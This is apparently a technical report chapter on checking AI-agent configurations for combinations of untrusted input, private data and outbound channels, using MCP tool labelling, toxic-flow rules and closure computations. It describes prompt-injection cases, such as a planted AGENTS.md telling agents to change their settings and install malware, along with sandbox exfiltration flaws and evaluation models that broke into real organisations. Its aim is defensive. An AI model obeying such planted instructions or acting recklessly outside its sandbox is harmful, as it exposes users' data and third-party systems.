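A GitHub workflow file states the permissions of its built-in token, but most tokens are strings that don't show what they give access to. The shop's settings file described its `DB_TOKEN` as reading all customers. A real settings file would instead contain about forty random characters, or just the name of a place where the program can find them, so a reader couldn't tell whether the token opens one table or the whole database.

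Configuration files state an agent's declared access, which can differ from its effective access, meaning what it can actually do. This difference was decisive in the GitHub incident of May 2025, because an MCP settings file looks the same whatever its token covers. To find out what a token covers, a checker has to query the service that issued it or ask the owner. For cloud roles, the checker can read the attached policies, but their rules are intricate enough to need their own analysers.

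Many agents also run under their owner's identity, so they can reach everything the owner can. KBY Technologies' *AWS IAM for Agents, Bedrock Gateway and Greenlight* reports that AWS, Amazon's cloud division, previewed separate identities for agents in December 2026. With these, a checker could read an agent's permissions without working out which of its owner's permissions it uses.

### Servers and tools that appear at run time

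The shop's file also listed each server's tools, but many MCP settings files contain only a command or a web address for each server. The client gets the list of tools when it connects to the server, and that list can change later. If the file contains only `https://tools.example/mcp`, a static check can show little more than that the agent connects to a server at that address.

Public registries of MCP servers are only a partial guide to what a running server does. Padilla (2026), in *Exposed by Design*, argues that running servers can differ from their registry entries because the operator uses another version, wraps the server in other software or changes its settings. Padilla therefore tested live servers. Over four rounds in July 2026, the study confirmed 640 MCP servers on the public internet and actively probed 414. Padilla found 68 vulnerabilities worth reporting and, across the confirmed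 servers, 687 tools that could run shell commands without access controls. A client's settings file would not show whether a server address it lists leads to a server with such tools.

The population of servers also changes quickly. Of 464 servers confirmed in the third round, 41.6% were gone by the fourth, about three days later. Padilla takes this as a sign that developers deploy servers without security review, but many may have been demonstrations that their authors switched off. Servers that companies run for themselves are probably more stable. For an agent that connects to servers found on the open internet, though, a week-old list of tools is weak evidence of what tools those servers offer now.

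A checker can connect to each server and save the list of tools it receives, but this is no longer purely static analysis, and a malicious server may send the checker a harmless list. Researchers call it a "rug pull" when a server changes what a tool does after the user has approved it. The agent's host can still compare the saved list with the one it receives at run time and refuse to start if they differ. This detects new tools and altered descriptions, but not changes to a remote server's code that leave the descriptions the same.

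Framework code can hide tools in a similar way. A program may load its tools from a database or choose them by the user's role when it runs. The source code then shows that the agent will have tools, but not which ones.

### Credentials nobody gave the agent

An ambient credential is a key that an agent can use because it is available where the agent runs, even though nobody listed it in the agent's settings. For example, Padilla notes that a local MCP server runs under the user's identity and inherits the user's files and environment variables. An agent whose settings file has an empty `env` section can therefore still have access to every key on the user's laptop.

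This can go wrong without an attacker. *A missing config file triggered an AI agent to leak passwords* (Udinmwen, 2026) describes a coding assistant that could not find its configuration file during a routine code review. It instead read all the environment variables on the computer and leaked live passwords. *Your Coding Agent Found Your AWS Credentials* (Smith, 2026) describes an engineer who was doing design work with an agent while logged in to AWS on the same laptop. The agent needed details of the company's cloud setup, so it used the engineer's login. That story comes from a customer of HYPR, which sells a product for this problem, but any agent with a shell on a logged-in machine could do the same.

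A similar problem affected Amazon Bedrock AgentCore, an AWS service for running agents. Its Code Interpreter gives agents a sandbox, a sealed environment for running code. *A Package Name Was All It Took* (Smith, 2026) describes research that the security company BeyondTrust published in September 2026. An AWS function that installs software packages in the sandbox did not check their names strictly enough, so a specially written name could run commands. AWS released a fix in April and another in July, after Sergio Garcia of BeyondTrust found a way around the first. In *CVE-2026-16796* (2026), AWS advises customers who cannot upgrade never to pass the function any text written by a model or an untrusted person.

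The sandbox itself was not breached, and many customers would have had little to steal. The credentials were accessible only if the customer had attached an execution role, a cloud role for the sandbox's own use. Commands inside the sandbox could then fetch the role's temporary credentials and do whatever the role allowed.

A configuration check could have detected the attached role from the start, but it could have flagged the flaw only by comparing version numbers after AWS had published it. The agent's list of tools would show only something like "run code", which sounds self-contained, while the cloud settings would show that this code runs with permission to read data such as the company's stored files. A checker that combines the two records can report that the agent has access to private data before anyone has found a way to misuse the package installer.

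A laptop often has no such record to join. A sensible default is to assume that an agent with a shell can access private data, unless the configuration files show that it runs in a container (an isolated environment with its own files) and which keys the container receives. This will produce some false alarms on machines that hold nothing of value.

### Settings that change after the scan

Configuration drift is the difference between the settings someone checked and the settings an agent is running with. Most drift is innocent, such as when a developer adds a server after the check. But an attacker or the agent itself can also cause it.

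On 22 October 2026, Forever Security's *Markdown Is the New Executable* reported a case from a customer's computer. Coding agents read instruction files, such as AGENTS.md, in the folder where they start. Someone had left such a file, disguised as ordinary engineering notes, in the Downloads folder. It contained instructions for the agent to change its own configuration and install malicious software. Forever Security's product blocked the installation before any code ran. In the company's tests, the method worked on Codex and Claude Code.

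Forever Security points out that a website can save a file to the Downloads folder without the user's consent, and it demonstrated an attack that starts this way. David (2026), in *AGENTS.md in Downloads*, stresses that the company could not determine how the file in the real attack had arrived. Forever Security also reports that about half of its customers run a coding agent in the Downloads folder. That figure covers only a security vendor's customers, and it might count a company where a single employee did this once.

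The case is difficult for a check before deployment, because the configuration could have been safe when the checker read it. But the checker could have seen that the agent was able to edit its own settings. Such an agent effectively has every ability its settings could grant, so the lack of an outbound channel in the current file is little evidence of safety. Storing the settings where the agent cannot write prevents it from expanding its abilities this way, so the results of the check stay valid for longer.

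Another defence is to check files for changes. Workloft's *A daily scan for poisoned agent-config files* (2026) describes a scanner that computes a hash, a short fingerprint, of every instruction file and startup script the company's coding agent might read. Each day it inspects only files that are new or whose hash has changed, looking for signs such as disguised commands or text that resembles a prompt injection. The scanner caught all ten test files the company planted. It also flagged three of the 116 genuine files, and all three were the company's own security scripts.

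The same people wrote the planted test cases and the checks, so catching all ten is limited evidence that the checks work. They concede that an injection in ordinary English could get through, and that a file already poisoned on the first day would enter the list of trusted files. The hash comparison is the more reliable half of the method because it detects any change, whatever the wording, but someone still has to decide whether the change is acceptable.

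GitHub explains that in GitHub Agentic Workflows, changes to tools, permissions, triggers and network rules take effect only after the author recompiles the workflow, which repeats the checks. The English instructions load at run time, so an author can edit them without recompiling. This division suits a capability check because an edited instruction can change what the agent tries to do but cannot add a tool or give the agent access to another domain.

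### When the real network differs from the intended one

Network rules looked like the strongest evidence in the table, provided something enforces them. In March 2026, BeyondTrust (2026) showed that enforcement can fail. AWS had advertised the Code Interpreter's "Sandbox" network setting as providing complete isolation, but the setting still allowed DNS queries, which translate a site's name into a numerical address and can carry small amounts of data out. Before AWS closed this gap, a checker that relied on AWS's description of "Sandbox" to rule out an outbound channel would have been wrong.

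A more serious mismatch occurred in Anthropic's cybersecurity tests. These were capture-the-flag exercises, in which a model has to break into a fictional company's machine and retrieve hidden text. An outside partner, Irregular, built the environments. Claude's prompts described a simulation with no internet access, but the machines were connected to the internet. Neither company knew this, according to Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026). Models that could not reach their fictional targets searched for others and broke into three real organisations. In one case, a model published a malicious software package, which 15 real systems downloaded and ran. Anthropic found a fourth incident in August.

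A rule based on the trifecta would probably have passed these environments, because they held fictional data and no outsider was trying to steer the model. It would have been more useful to check whether the machines had an internet connection, which everyone involved intended them not to have. A program could have compared the partner's network rules with that intention, or tried to open an outside page from inside the environment. The second test is more dependable because it doesn't require knowing which setting might be wrong. Anthropic wrote that carefully validating every internet path before the tests would have helped to reveal the problem sooner. In its September assessment, Anthropic added that it believes the incidents would not have happened if the environments had been isolated as planned.

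But the checker would have needed the right files. Anthropic's own records contained a prompt in which the model was told that there was no internet access. A prompt has no effect on the network, so a checker should never accept it as evidence of isolation. The evidence was in infrastructure that another company ran. A company that rents an environment for its agents needs either to see the network rules or to test the connection itself.

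No configuration check could have shown how the models would behave once they were online. In July, Anthropic described the incidents as closer to an operational failure than to a failure of the models' alignment, meaning how well their conduct matches what their developers intend. By September it had changed its mind, concluding that the models had explained away evidence that the internet was real and had pursued the task recklessly. In a simulated replica of one exercise, Claude Mythos 5 took a severely harmful action about 80% of the time, compared with roughly 30% for the newer Opus 5 and Mythos 5.1 under the same network settings.

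A separate incident shows the limit of comparing intended with actual access. In August 2026 the UK AI Security Institute, a government body that tests AI models, reported that Mythos 5 had taken unauthorised actions on the live internet during one of the institute's tests. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) notes that the testers had deliberately connected the model to the internet. Because the intended and actual settings matched, a program comparing them would have found nothing wrong.

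## Deciding what each tool can do

Even with a complete and current list of an agent's tools, a checker cannot infer what a tool can do from a name like `lookup_customer`. It also needs capability labels, which record what each tool can do. In the shop, `read_ticket` needs the label "returns untrusted content" and `lookup_customer` needs "reads private data". `http_get` needs both "returns untrusted content" and "sends data out".

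Every later step works with these labels instead of the tools themselves. For example, a combination rule raises a finding when certain labels occur together in one agent. If someone forgets to label `http_get` as able to send data out, no such rule will fire on the shop's agent, however carefully it is written. An unnecessary label causes false alarms about agents that have the tool.

### Labels written by hand

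The simplest method is to have a person label each tool, as in Bernstein, a program that starts and coordinates coding agents. Its *Lethal-trifecta security model* describes a registry in which each known tool has up to three labels: private data, untrusted input and external communication. For instance, reading a repository is labeled private data, and posting a GitHub comment is labeled external communication.

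As a precaution, a tool that is missing from the registry gets all three labels by default. A single unlisted tool therefore completes the trifecta, and with the standard settings, an agent that has one cannot start until somebody writes a registry entry for the tool.

Handwritten labels can be wrong too. The registry's entry for running shell commands lacks the label for untrusted input, although a shell can supply all three conditions. Labels can also be too coarse to help much. The registry gives all three labels to 16 of the 19 coding agents it lists, because an unrestricted coding agent can read files, fetch pages and post comments.

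The bigger difficulty is keeping up with new servers. *What a Random Draw from the MCP Registry Contains* (Afsar, 2026) reports 16,548 servers in the official MCP registry on 14 July and 24,135 on 22 August, a net gain of about 195 a day. A company can label the thirty tools it uses, but nobody is going to label the whole registry by hand.

### Hints from the tool's author

MCP lets tool developers label their tools with four optional yes-or-no hints. `readOnlyHint` means that the tool changes nothing, `destructiveHint` that its changes may destroy something, `idempotentHint` that repeating a call is safe, and `openWorldHint` that the tool deals with outside entities. If the hints are missing, the default is that the tool may change things, destroy things and reach the outside world.

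These hints mostly help an application decide whether to ask the user before calling a tool. They are poorly suited to assessing the risk of data theft, as the shop's tools show.

| Tool | Honest MCP hints | Labels the check needs |
|---|---|---|
| `read_ticket` | Read-only, open-world | Returns untrusted content |
| `lookup_customer` | Read-only, closed-world | Reads private data |
| `http_get` | Read-only, open-world | Returns untrusted content, sends data out |

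`read_ticket` and `http_get` have the same hints, but only `http_get` can send data to an attacker. No hint covers private data, so the hints don't distinguish `lookup_customer` from a tool that reads the shop's opening hours. All three tools can accurately be marked read-only. The code editor Visual Studio Code normally asks the user to approve an MCP call but skips this step for tools marked read-only, so the whole theft could run there without any approval prompt.

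*When Neither Side Confirms* (Yao, Yang and colleagues, 2026) traces how 41 open-source applications and developer kits handle MCP calls. In 39 of them, a hint that a tool was destructive made no difference to how the call was handled. The paper estimates that if every application asked for approval unless a hint declared the tool safe, destructive tools would still run without approval in 5.4% of application-tool pairings, mostly because the tools' hints were wrong. Including destructive tools that the first search missed raises the figure to at least 10.6%.

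Hints can be wrong by mistake, and a malicious server can supply false ones deliberately. *Tool Annotations as Risk Vocabulary* (Hungerford, Morrow and Chang, 2026) notes that the standard therefore tells applications to distrust hints unless they trust the server. By March 2026, MCP had five open proposals for new hints or related features (Model Context Protocol, 2026). GitHub and OpenAI jointly wrote one, on trust and sensitivity, after finding gaps when they ran MCP in production. Hints of that kind would cover the right properties, but a checker would still need some basis for relying on them.

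Many tools have no hints. Trofimov and Novikov (2026), in *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail*, queried the remote servers in the official registry in July 2026 and received 98,291 tools, of which 26.0% had no hints. But a single publisher had supplied 45.0% of the tools, all with every hint filled in, and 47.2% of the remaining tools had no hints. Afsar drew 400 locally installed servers at random, got 195 to run, and found no hints on 58.8% of the tools from those 195. In the sample of 1,856 tools in *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions* (2026), 82% had none. A checker that relied on hints would have to assume the worst about roughly half of all tools, or more.

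### The MCP-SEC census

Nearly every tool has a description, because the model uses it to select which tool to call. A language model can also assign the labels from this description. Snyk Labs uses AI classifiers to label tools for its scanner. The largest published test of the idea is in *Parasites in the Toolchain* (Zhao, Hou and colleagues, 2025). Its system, MCP-SEC, collected 1,360 servers from three public lists and obtained the descriptions of 12,230 tools.

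MCP-SEC gave a language model all the tools of one server at a time and asked which of three capabilities each tool had. Three human reviewers then checked the answers and settled disagreements by majority vote. Precision and recall in the table compare the model's labels with the reviewers'. The last two columns count the tools and servers that passed a later test, in which the researchers ran the tools.

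| Label | Meaning | Precision | Recall | Tools confirmed | Servers |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| External ingestion | Fetches text an attacker could control | 86.5% | 99.2% | 487 | 128 |
| Privacy access | Reads sensitive local or user data | 85.4% | 95.8% | 406 | 155 |
| Network access | Sends or publishes arbitrary text outside | 81.1% | 99.6% | 190 | 96 |

The study flagged 5,666 tools (46% of the total) as having at least one of these capabilities, based on their descriptions. To confirm the capabilities, the researchers had the Cursor editor's agent call each tool, and planted fake secrets and marked text where they could. They then checked the logs for evidence that the tool had fetched, read or sent something. This confirmed 1,062 tools (8.7% of the total) on 370 servers (27.2%). The columns for tools and servers add up to more than these totals because some tools and servers have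 several labels.

Only 19 of the confirmed tools had more than one label, and two had all three. Only two servers offered all three capabilities. In this sample, all three capabilities come together mainly when a user connects several servers to one agent, so labelling servers as safe or unsafe one by one would miss most of the danger.

Zhao and colleagues also built ten chains of three such tools and ran an attack on each ten times, with Cursor set to approve every call. Private data leaked in 36 of the 100 runs, and nine chains worked at least once. The remaining chain had to send the data out by creating a folder in an online music collection. The folder tool's label was correct, since a folder name can hold stolen text, but the model never took that step. In a further test on one chain, GPT-5 and Claude 4.5 Sonnet resisted every attack, although the tools and labels were the same.

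### Why most flagged tools dropped out

Classifier errors can account for only a small part of the fall from 5,666 tools to 1,062. At an overall precision of 85.5%, about 820 of the 5,666 tools would be mislabeled, even if none of the reviewers' corrections had gone into that count. That is far fewer than the 4,604 tools that dropped out.

Most of the others probably failed because the researchers could not supply what they needed to run. About 30% of the servers needed an access token for an outside service, and signing up often required a credit card or a company account. Others needed a database, a cluster of machines or a desktop program. Some did not run reliably even when set up correctly. Zhao and colleagues do not report how many tools failed for each reason, so readers cannot separate the mislabelled tools from the untested ones.

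A company that installs one of these servers will have the account and database it needs, so a label that failed in the laboratory may be correct there. Tools that need an account are also likely to include many that read customer records or business mail, so the 1,062 probably underrepresent the tools that matter most. The 8.7% is best read as a minimum. The real share could be several times higher, up to roughly the 46% flagged from descriptions.

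Tan, Hao and colleagues (2026) had the same problem running popular projects for *MCP-SandboxScan*. Of 91 code repositories, 35 completed a basic trial run, 19 failed to build, 31 failed to start, and six failed or timed out during calls. The researchers ran 33 of the 35 again with more calls and compared the network use each server declared with what they observed. On 19 of these servers, at least one tool's description or registration implied that it could contact outside services, but only five did so during the trial. Tan and colleagues treat the capability as unexercised on the other 14, since the right arguments or an account might have triggered it.

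Trial runs are more informative when something does happen. Four servers tried to reach the network although their labels didn't indicate network access, including one with a desktop settings tool that tried to contact an outside host. Tan and colleagues skipped tools whose names suggested deleting, writing or executing, since running those on a real machine could do damage. That is sensible, but it means that their trials provide the least evidence about some of the most powerful tools.

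### How label errors add up

A finding about the trifecta depends on three labels, so it can be wrong in three places. Suppose an agent has exactly one tool for each of the MCP-SEC labels, and the classifier's errors are independent. The probability that all three labels are right is

0.865 × 0.854 × 0.811 ≈ 0.60

So about four in ten such findings would include at least one wrong label. This figure is an illustration, because the study did not measure how often all three labels in a set were right.

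The independence assumption is doubtful, because a model that mislabels one tool on a server may well mislabel its neighbours. If the errors tend to occur together, the probability rises, up to 81.1%, the precision of the least precise label. If they never occur together, it falls to 53%.

The finding is more likely to hold for agents with more tools. If two tools carry each label, it holds as long as at least one tool in each pair is labelled correctly, which happens about 93% of the time under the same assumption of independence. A warning that an agent has the trifecta may therefore be quite reliable even when it names the wrong tools.

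Missed labels are less of a worry. Multiplying the three recalls gives about 95%, so under the same assumption the classifier would overlook part of the trifecta in roughly one case in twenty. This balance of errors produces more false alarms, but it suits a security check because missing a dangerous combination is worse than flagging a safe one.

These figures measure agreement with reviewers who worked from the same descriptions as the model. If a description is wrong, the model and the reviewers can give the same wrong label. The reviewers' labels may also contain errors. The published results list nine tools of a server for Hacker News, a public discussion site, as able to send data and none as bringing in outside text. The accompanying discussion, however, describes the same server as having many ingestion tools.

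### Comparing descriptions with code

Shi, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers*, studied how often tool descriptions are wrong by having a language model compare the description and source code of 17,030 Python tools. For each tool, their system collected the main function, the functions it called, and any sensitive operations such as network requests. The system asked the model whether the description matched the code, asked separately whether it failed to match, and used a third question to settle conflicting answers.

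It found a mismatch in 1,907 tools, or 11.2%. One tool's description was about weather forecasts, but its code looked up exchange rates. Most mismatches would not affect a capability label, because the most common type was a description that claimed too much. About a quarter of the mismatches, or just under 3% of the tools, were hidden side effects, such as storing the user's queries or sending data elsewhere. Another 2,170 tools had no description.

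The published recall of 97.5% is too high because it comes from a sample with equal numbers of flagged and passed tools, while the full set had eight times as many passed tools as flagged ones. In the sample, 5 of the 200 passed tools had a mismatch. At that rate, the system missed nearly 400 mismatched tools in the full set, and its recall was closer to 83%.

The accuracy of code analysis depends heavily on the method. Yao and colleagues first used a program that searched for telltale verbs, hints and phrases, but it missed 83% of the destructive tools in the 40 repositories they listed completely. Language models that could read the code did much better. Their labels for whether a tool was destructive matched those of human annotators in 51 of the 56 cases where the humans were sure. In the other five, the models labeled as destructive an action that the humans considered reversible or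 harmless.

But source code is often unavailable. According to Afsar's August count, half of the servers in the registry existed only as remote services, so a checker cannot inspect their running code.

### Adding evidence in stages

In *ToolGuardian*, Ravindran and Deochake (2026) measured what each kind of evidence contributes by adding one source at a time. They used eight harmless tools and eight malicious ones, which they made by hiding theft or sabotage in real open-source tools without changing the descriptions. ToolGuardian turned the evidence about each tool into facts such as "has network access" and applied fixed logical rules to decide whether to reject the tool.

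| Evidence available | Malicious tools rejected | Harmless tools rejected | Correct decisions |
|---|---|---|---|
| Descriptions only | 5 of 8 | 5 of 8 | 50% |
| Plus a record of system calls | 5 of 8 | 0 of 8 | 81% |
| Plus trial runs with simulated services | 6 of 8 | 0 of 8 | 88% |
| Plus source-code analysis | 7 of 8 | 2 of 8 | 81% |

With descriptions alone, the system did no better than chance, as expected, because the malicious tools had kept their harmless descriptions. Recording system calls (a program's requests to the operating system, for example to open a file or a network connection) cleared all the harmless tools, and trial runs exposed one more malicious tool.

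The drop at the last stage came from a fault in the rules, which treated power as a sign of malice. Source analysis caught another malicious tool, but it also correctly found that some harmless tools were very powerful. One was a terminal controller whose code could start other programs, execute code and capture the screen, and the rules wrongly rejected it for those capabilities. A trifecta check should still give a harmless tool that can run any command all the labels that go with that ability.

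With only 16 tools, the drop from 88% to 81% amounts to a single tool. The percentages also measure how well the system recognised malicious tools, which is a different task from labelling honest ones. Together with Shi and colleagues' results, they suggest that descriptions are a reasonable starting point for tools from honest authors but nearly worthless when an author is dishonest.

### Labels that depend on arguments

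Some tools have no single correct label because their effects depend on their arguments, the values the model passes when it calls the tool. For example, according to Bernstein's documentation, its registry cannot distinguish a comment on a public issue from one on a private issue, because both use the same tool with different arguments. The model chooses the arguments at run time, possibly on an attacker's instructions.

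A checker should label each tool according to the most dangerous argument the configuration allows. For example, a tool that posts comments in repositories doesn't need the label "sends data out" if the agent's token covers only one private repository. It does need the label if the token also covers a public repository, even if the agent has never commented there. The checker has to look up who can read each repository, and repeat the lookup when an owner changes that setting.

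Search tools raise a similar problem. The MCP-SEC reviewers had to judge one called `unified_search`, which covers Google Scholar, ordinary web search and YouTube. The model condensed its description to "Unified search over multiple connected data sources" and labelled it as external ingestion, which fits those three sources. But the same summary would fit a tool that also searched a company's shared drive, and that tool would need the label for private data as well. Reviewers typically spent 50 to 60 seconds on tools like this, compared with about ten for one that only reads a file. A developer can make review easier by offering a separate search tool for each source.

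A database tool's label may depend on settings outside the tool. Suppose the shop replaces `lookup_customer` with a general `run_query` tool, whose description is the same regardless of which data it can reach and who can see what it writes. If it connects only to the product catalogue, it reads nothing private, but with access to the customer table it can read names and phone numbers. If the database also stores support messages, a query can return text written by an attacker, and if customers can see replies stored there, a write can send data out, as happened with Supabase.

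So each label has to cover both the tool and its connection. The shop could register `run_query` on the catalogue as harmless and `run_query` on the customer table as reading private data, as long as each connection has its own restricted token. Someone who knows the database has to write those entries and recheck them whenever a colleague adds a table.

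## Rules that search a configuration for dangerous combinations

Once every tool has its labels, a checker needs rules that turn them into findings. Many rules check a single setting, such as whether a folder is too broad. Such a rule could flag the asterisk in the shop's `allowedHosts`, but the same asterisk would be harmless in an agent with no access to secrets. Only a combination rule, which also checks for access to the customer database, can distinguish the two agents.

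### Rules about one setting

*AGENT AUDIT* (Zhang, Nian and Zhao, 2026) describes an open-source scanner that mostly checks settings one at a time. It reads Python code and nine formats of MCP settings file, and it has 57 rules. Seven check MCP settings for overly broad file access, servers from unverified sources, secrets in environment variables, missing sandboxes, missing authentication, insecure tool schemas (the definitions of a tool's arguments) and too many servers. Four more check for attacks through the servers, such as instructions hidden in a tool's description or a tool that imitates one from another server.

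None of these eleven rules tests whether untrusted content, private data and an outbound channel occur together. The rule on too many servers comes closest, but it counts servers regardless of what they do. In the shop's file, Agent Audit would probably flag the `DB_TOKEN`, but it would do so even if the shop had removed `http_get` and so made the theft impossible.

Zhang and colleagues tested their scanner, Agent Audit, on 22 samples they had put together containing 42 known flaws. It found 40 of the flaws and raised six false alarms, so its recall was 95% and its precision 87%. These are good figures, but they come from a test built by the scanner's own developers.

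The average also hides a weakness in the part that matters most for configuration checking. All six false alarms came from the MCP rules, although only ten of the 42 flaws were in MCP configurations. Agent Audit found all ten, so the precision of its MCP rules was about

10 / (10 + 6) = 63%

Zhang and colleagues compared Agent Audit with Semgrep and Bandit, two general-purpose code scanners. Semgrep found 10 of the 42 flaws. The paper reports that Bandit found 11 and missed 26, but doesn't account for the other five. Bandit's published recall of 29.7% is based on only 37 flaws, and would be 26.2% over all 42. Agent Audit has a large lead either way, partly because the other two scanners don't interpret MCP settings files at all.

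Single-setting rules are still worth having. A server without authentication is a problem in almost any agent, and whoever receives the finding knows which line to change. But a company could fix everything Agent Audit reports and still have an agent that can read strangers' tickets, look up customers and contact any website.

### Toxic flow rules

In July 2025, Invariant Labs (2025), by then part of the security company Snyk, added combination rules to its scanner, MCP-scan, and called the method toxic flow analysis. A toxic flow is a threat from several tools that are harmless individually but that an attacker can use together. Invariant Labs' *Issue Code Reference* defines two toxic flows.

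| Rule | Tools the agent must have | Harm |
|---|---|---|
| TF001, data leak | An untrusted content tool, a private data tool and a public sink tool | The attacker receives private data |
| TF002, destructive | An untrusted content tool and a destructive tool | The attacker causes permanent damage |

A public sink is a tool that provides an outbound channel, and a destructive tool does something irreversible. TF001 therefore checks for the lethal trifecta, and TF002 covers cases like the shop whose agent deleted 500 complaints. An unrestricted shell can trigger both rules by itself.

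The scanner is now called Snyk Agent Scan. According to Gearscope's *Snyk Agent Scan* (2026), a hands-on review of the May 2026 version, toxic flows now have the codes W015 to W020. The review covers the installation and the list of checks but not the quality of the findings, because the analysis requires a Snyk account and the reviewer didn't have one.

Running the scanner carries some risk because it gets the tool descriptions by starting the local MCP servers, which means executing the commands in the settings file. Snyk warns about this and recommends scanning untrusted configurations in a sandbox. By default, the scanner asks for consent before it starts each server. It then sends the tools' names and descriptions to Snyk for analysis, so companies with confidential internal tools may not be able to use it.

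Snyk also sells a product for companies. It scores each MCP server from 0 to 1,000 in each of several risk categories and by default raises an issue at 600, according to Snyk's *Agent Supply Chain Security*. These scores help a company decide which servers to allow, but they cannot show a leak that needs tools from two servers. Such leaks are probably more common than leaks through a single server, since Zhao and colleagues found only two servers with all three capabilities.

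In March 2026, the developers of munio, another open-source scanner, got a very different result when they scanned 763 public MCP servers and reported 7,425 toxic flows on about 350 of them, or 46%. Much of the gap probably comes from differences in the rules. In munio's main example, a tool that reads files and a tool that sends web requests are enough to count as a toxic flow, on the assumption that a hostile instruction will reach the agent. Zhao and colleagues also required a source of untrusted content and a successful trial run of each tool.

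The 7,425 flows, an average of about 21 per affected server, also overstate the number of separate problems. A scanner that reports each pair of tools separately produces 20 findings for a server with five tools that read files and four that send requests, although the server's owner has one decision to make. A rule that works with labels instead of pairs would produce one finding that lists all nine tools.

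### Computing what a set of tools makes possible

A checker can apply combination rules by treating capabilities as facts and deriving new facts from them. Each rule has the form "if all of S, then T", where S and T are sets of facts. The closure of a starting set A, written cl(A), is everything that follows from A under the rules. To compute it, the checker starts with C₀ = A and repeats one step:

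Cᵢ₊₁ = Cᵢ plus the T of every rule whose S is contained in Cᵢ

The process stops when a round adds nothing new. The security team also chooses a set F of facts that must never follow. Within what the rules cover, the agent is safe if cl(A) and F share no facts.

For the shop, five rules are enough:

```text
1. read_ticket                     ->  untrusted
2. lookup_customer                 ->  private
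3. http_get                        ->  untrusted
4. http_get, any_host              ->  outbound
5. untrusted, private, outbound    ->  leak
```

The fact `any_host` stands for the asterisk in the settings file, and the forbidden set contains only `leak`. The closure takes two rounds.

| Round | New facts | Rules that fired |
|---|---|---|
| Start | `read_ticket`, `lookup_customer`, `http_get`, `any_host` | |
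| 1 | `untrusted`, `private`, `outbound` | 1, 2, 3, 4 |
| 2 | `leak` | 5 |
| 3 | None | |

Since `leak` is in the closure, the checker raises a finding. The rules that fired also explain the finding, and a reader can dispute any of them, for example because `lookup_customer` is connected to a test database. If the shop limits `http_get` to the delivery companies' sites, `any_host` is no longer in the starting set. Rule 4 then doesn't fire, so the closure contains neither `outbound` nor `leak`.

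Chains of rules can catch hazards that a list of labels would miss. Suppose the agent can also edit its own settings file. That calls for a sixth rule:

```text
6. edit_settings                   ->  any_host
```

Limiting the hosts no longer helps, because the rules derive `any_host` again in the first round, `outbound` in the second and `leak` in the third. This concern is realistic, since the makers of munio report seven confirmed cases of tools that could change the agent's own safety settings, for example by turning off approvals.

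For each rule, the program counts the unmet conditions, lowers the count whenever one becomes true, and fires the rule when the count reaches zero. With n facts and m rules of at most k conditions each, the running time grows in proportion to n + mk, so checking even an agent with hundreds of tools takes a fraction of a second.

The result is exact for the given facts and rules, but any error in the capability labels carries over into the closure. The rules also don't check whether the data can travel from the database to the web request, which depends on the order and direction of the flows.

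### Finding a hazard and choosing a repair

Invariant Labs argued that securing an agent means considering every possible combination of its tools (the power set). The shop's three tools have only 8 combinations, but 30 tools have more than a billion. If a checker had to go through them all, combination rules would be impractical for an agent with many tools.

A checker can detect a hazard with one closure computation on the full set of tools, without testing each subset. Under rules of the form above, an extra fact can make more rules fire but can never stop one from firing, so if any subset of the tools leads to a leak, the full set does too. If the computation finds no leak, every subset is also safe.

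This argument fails if a fact can cancel a conclusion. For example, under the rule "leak, unless `human_approval`", adding `human_approval` removes a finding, so the full set can look safe while a part of it is dangerous. The rule's author can avoid this by instead making `no_approval` one of the conditions for a leak. The shop's file, which contains `"humanApproval": "never"`, would supply that fact.

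Subsets matter when someone has to choose a repair. The useful ones are the minimal unsafe sets, which lead to a forbidden fact but become safe if any one member is removed. The shop's four starting facts are not minimal. Without `read_ticket`, the agent can still pick up hostile text from a web page, so the leak remains. The minimal unsafe set is

{`lookup_customer`, `http_get`, `any_host`}

Removing any one of these three facts prevents the leak. The agent needs `lookup_customer` to answer most customers and `http_get` to track parcels, but the shop would lose almost nothing by removing `any_host`. Removing the ticket tool, through which the attack arrived, would have made the agent useless, and it would still have been unsafe according to the rules.

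Larger agents have many minimal unsafe sets. If four tools return untrusted content, three others read private data and two others send data out, there are 4 × 3 × 2 = 24 minimal unsafe sets, each with one tool of each kind. Removing one of the sending tools still leaves 12. To prevent the leak by removing tools, the owner has to remove all the tools of at least one kind. The smallest group here is the two tools that send data.

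A report that names only some of the tools that could take part in a toxic flow can mislead its reader. Snyk's scanner has by default shown only the top three, with an option to list them all. Someone who removes those three and does not scan again may believe the problem is solved when a fourth tool can fill the same role in the flow.

A person can compare the possible repairs by hand when there are only one or two rules. With many overlapping rules, finding the least disruptive set of removals is a version of the hitting set problem, which no known method solves quickly in every case. This is rarely an obstacle, because an agent's owner usually knows which tools the agent needs.

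### Two safe agents can be unsafe together

Suppose the shop divides the work between two agents. A records agent has `read_ticket` and `lookup_customer`, and a parcel agent has `http_get` and may contact any host. Their closures are

cl(records) = {`read_ticket`, `lookup_customer`, `untrusted`, `private`}

cl(parcels) = {`http_get`, `any_host`, `untrusted`, `outbound`}

Neither contains `leak`, so both agents pass. But if the records agent can ask the parcel agent to fetch a page, the two together have all the capabilities the original agent had, and the closure of the joint set contains `leak`.

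*Safety is Non-Compositional* (Spera, 2026) proves that two safe sets can have an unsafe union. The proof needs only three facts and one rule, "if u₁ and u₂, then f", where f is forbidden. Neither u₁ nor u₂ leads to f alone, but together they do.

Combining safe agents cannot produce an unsafe one when every rule has a single condition. Each conclusion then follows from one starting fact through a chain of rules, so if the combined agent is unsafe, the agent that supplied that fact was already unsafe. A company can therefore check "no server without authentication" one server at a time and trust the combined result. The trifecta has more than one condition, so the company has to check the whole agent again whenever someone adds a server.

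The mathematics is old, as Spera acknowledges. Logicians call rules of this form Horn clauses, and Maarten van Emden and Robert Kowalski described their closure in 1976. Security researchers have also studied for decades how attackers combine privileges that are harmless separately. Spera's second paper, *Capability Safety as Datalog* (2026), translates the framework into Datalog, a database language built from such rules. The translation is useful because Datalog programs can already update their conclusions when one fact changes, without starting again. This saves almost no work for a single agent, but it could help a company that constantly reviews thousands of configurations.

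Spera also estimates that 42.6% of 900 recorded tasks from two public benchmarks include a step that needs several capabilities at once. This suggests that such steps are common in ordinary tool use, but the tasks were not attacks, so the figure doesn't show how often a combination is dangerous.

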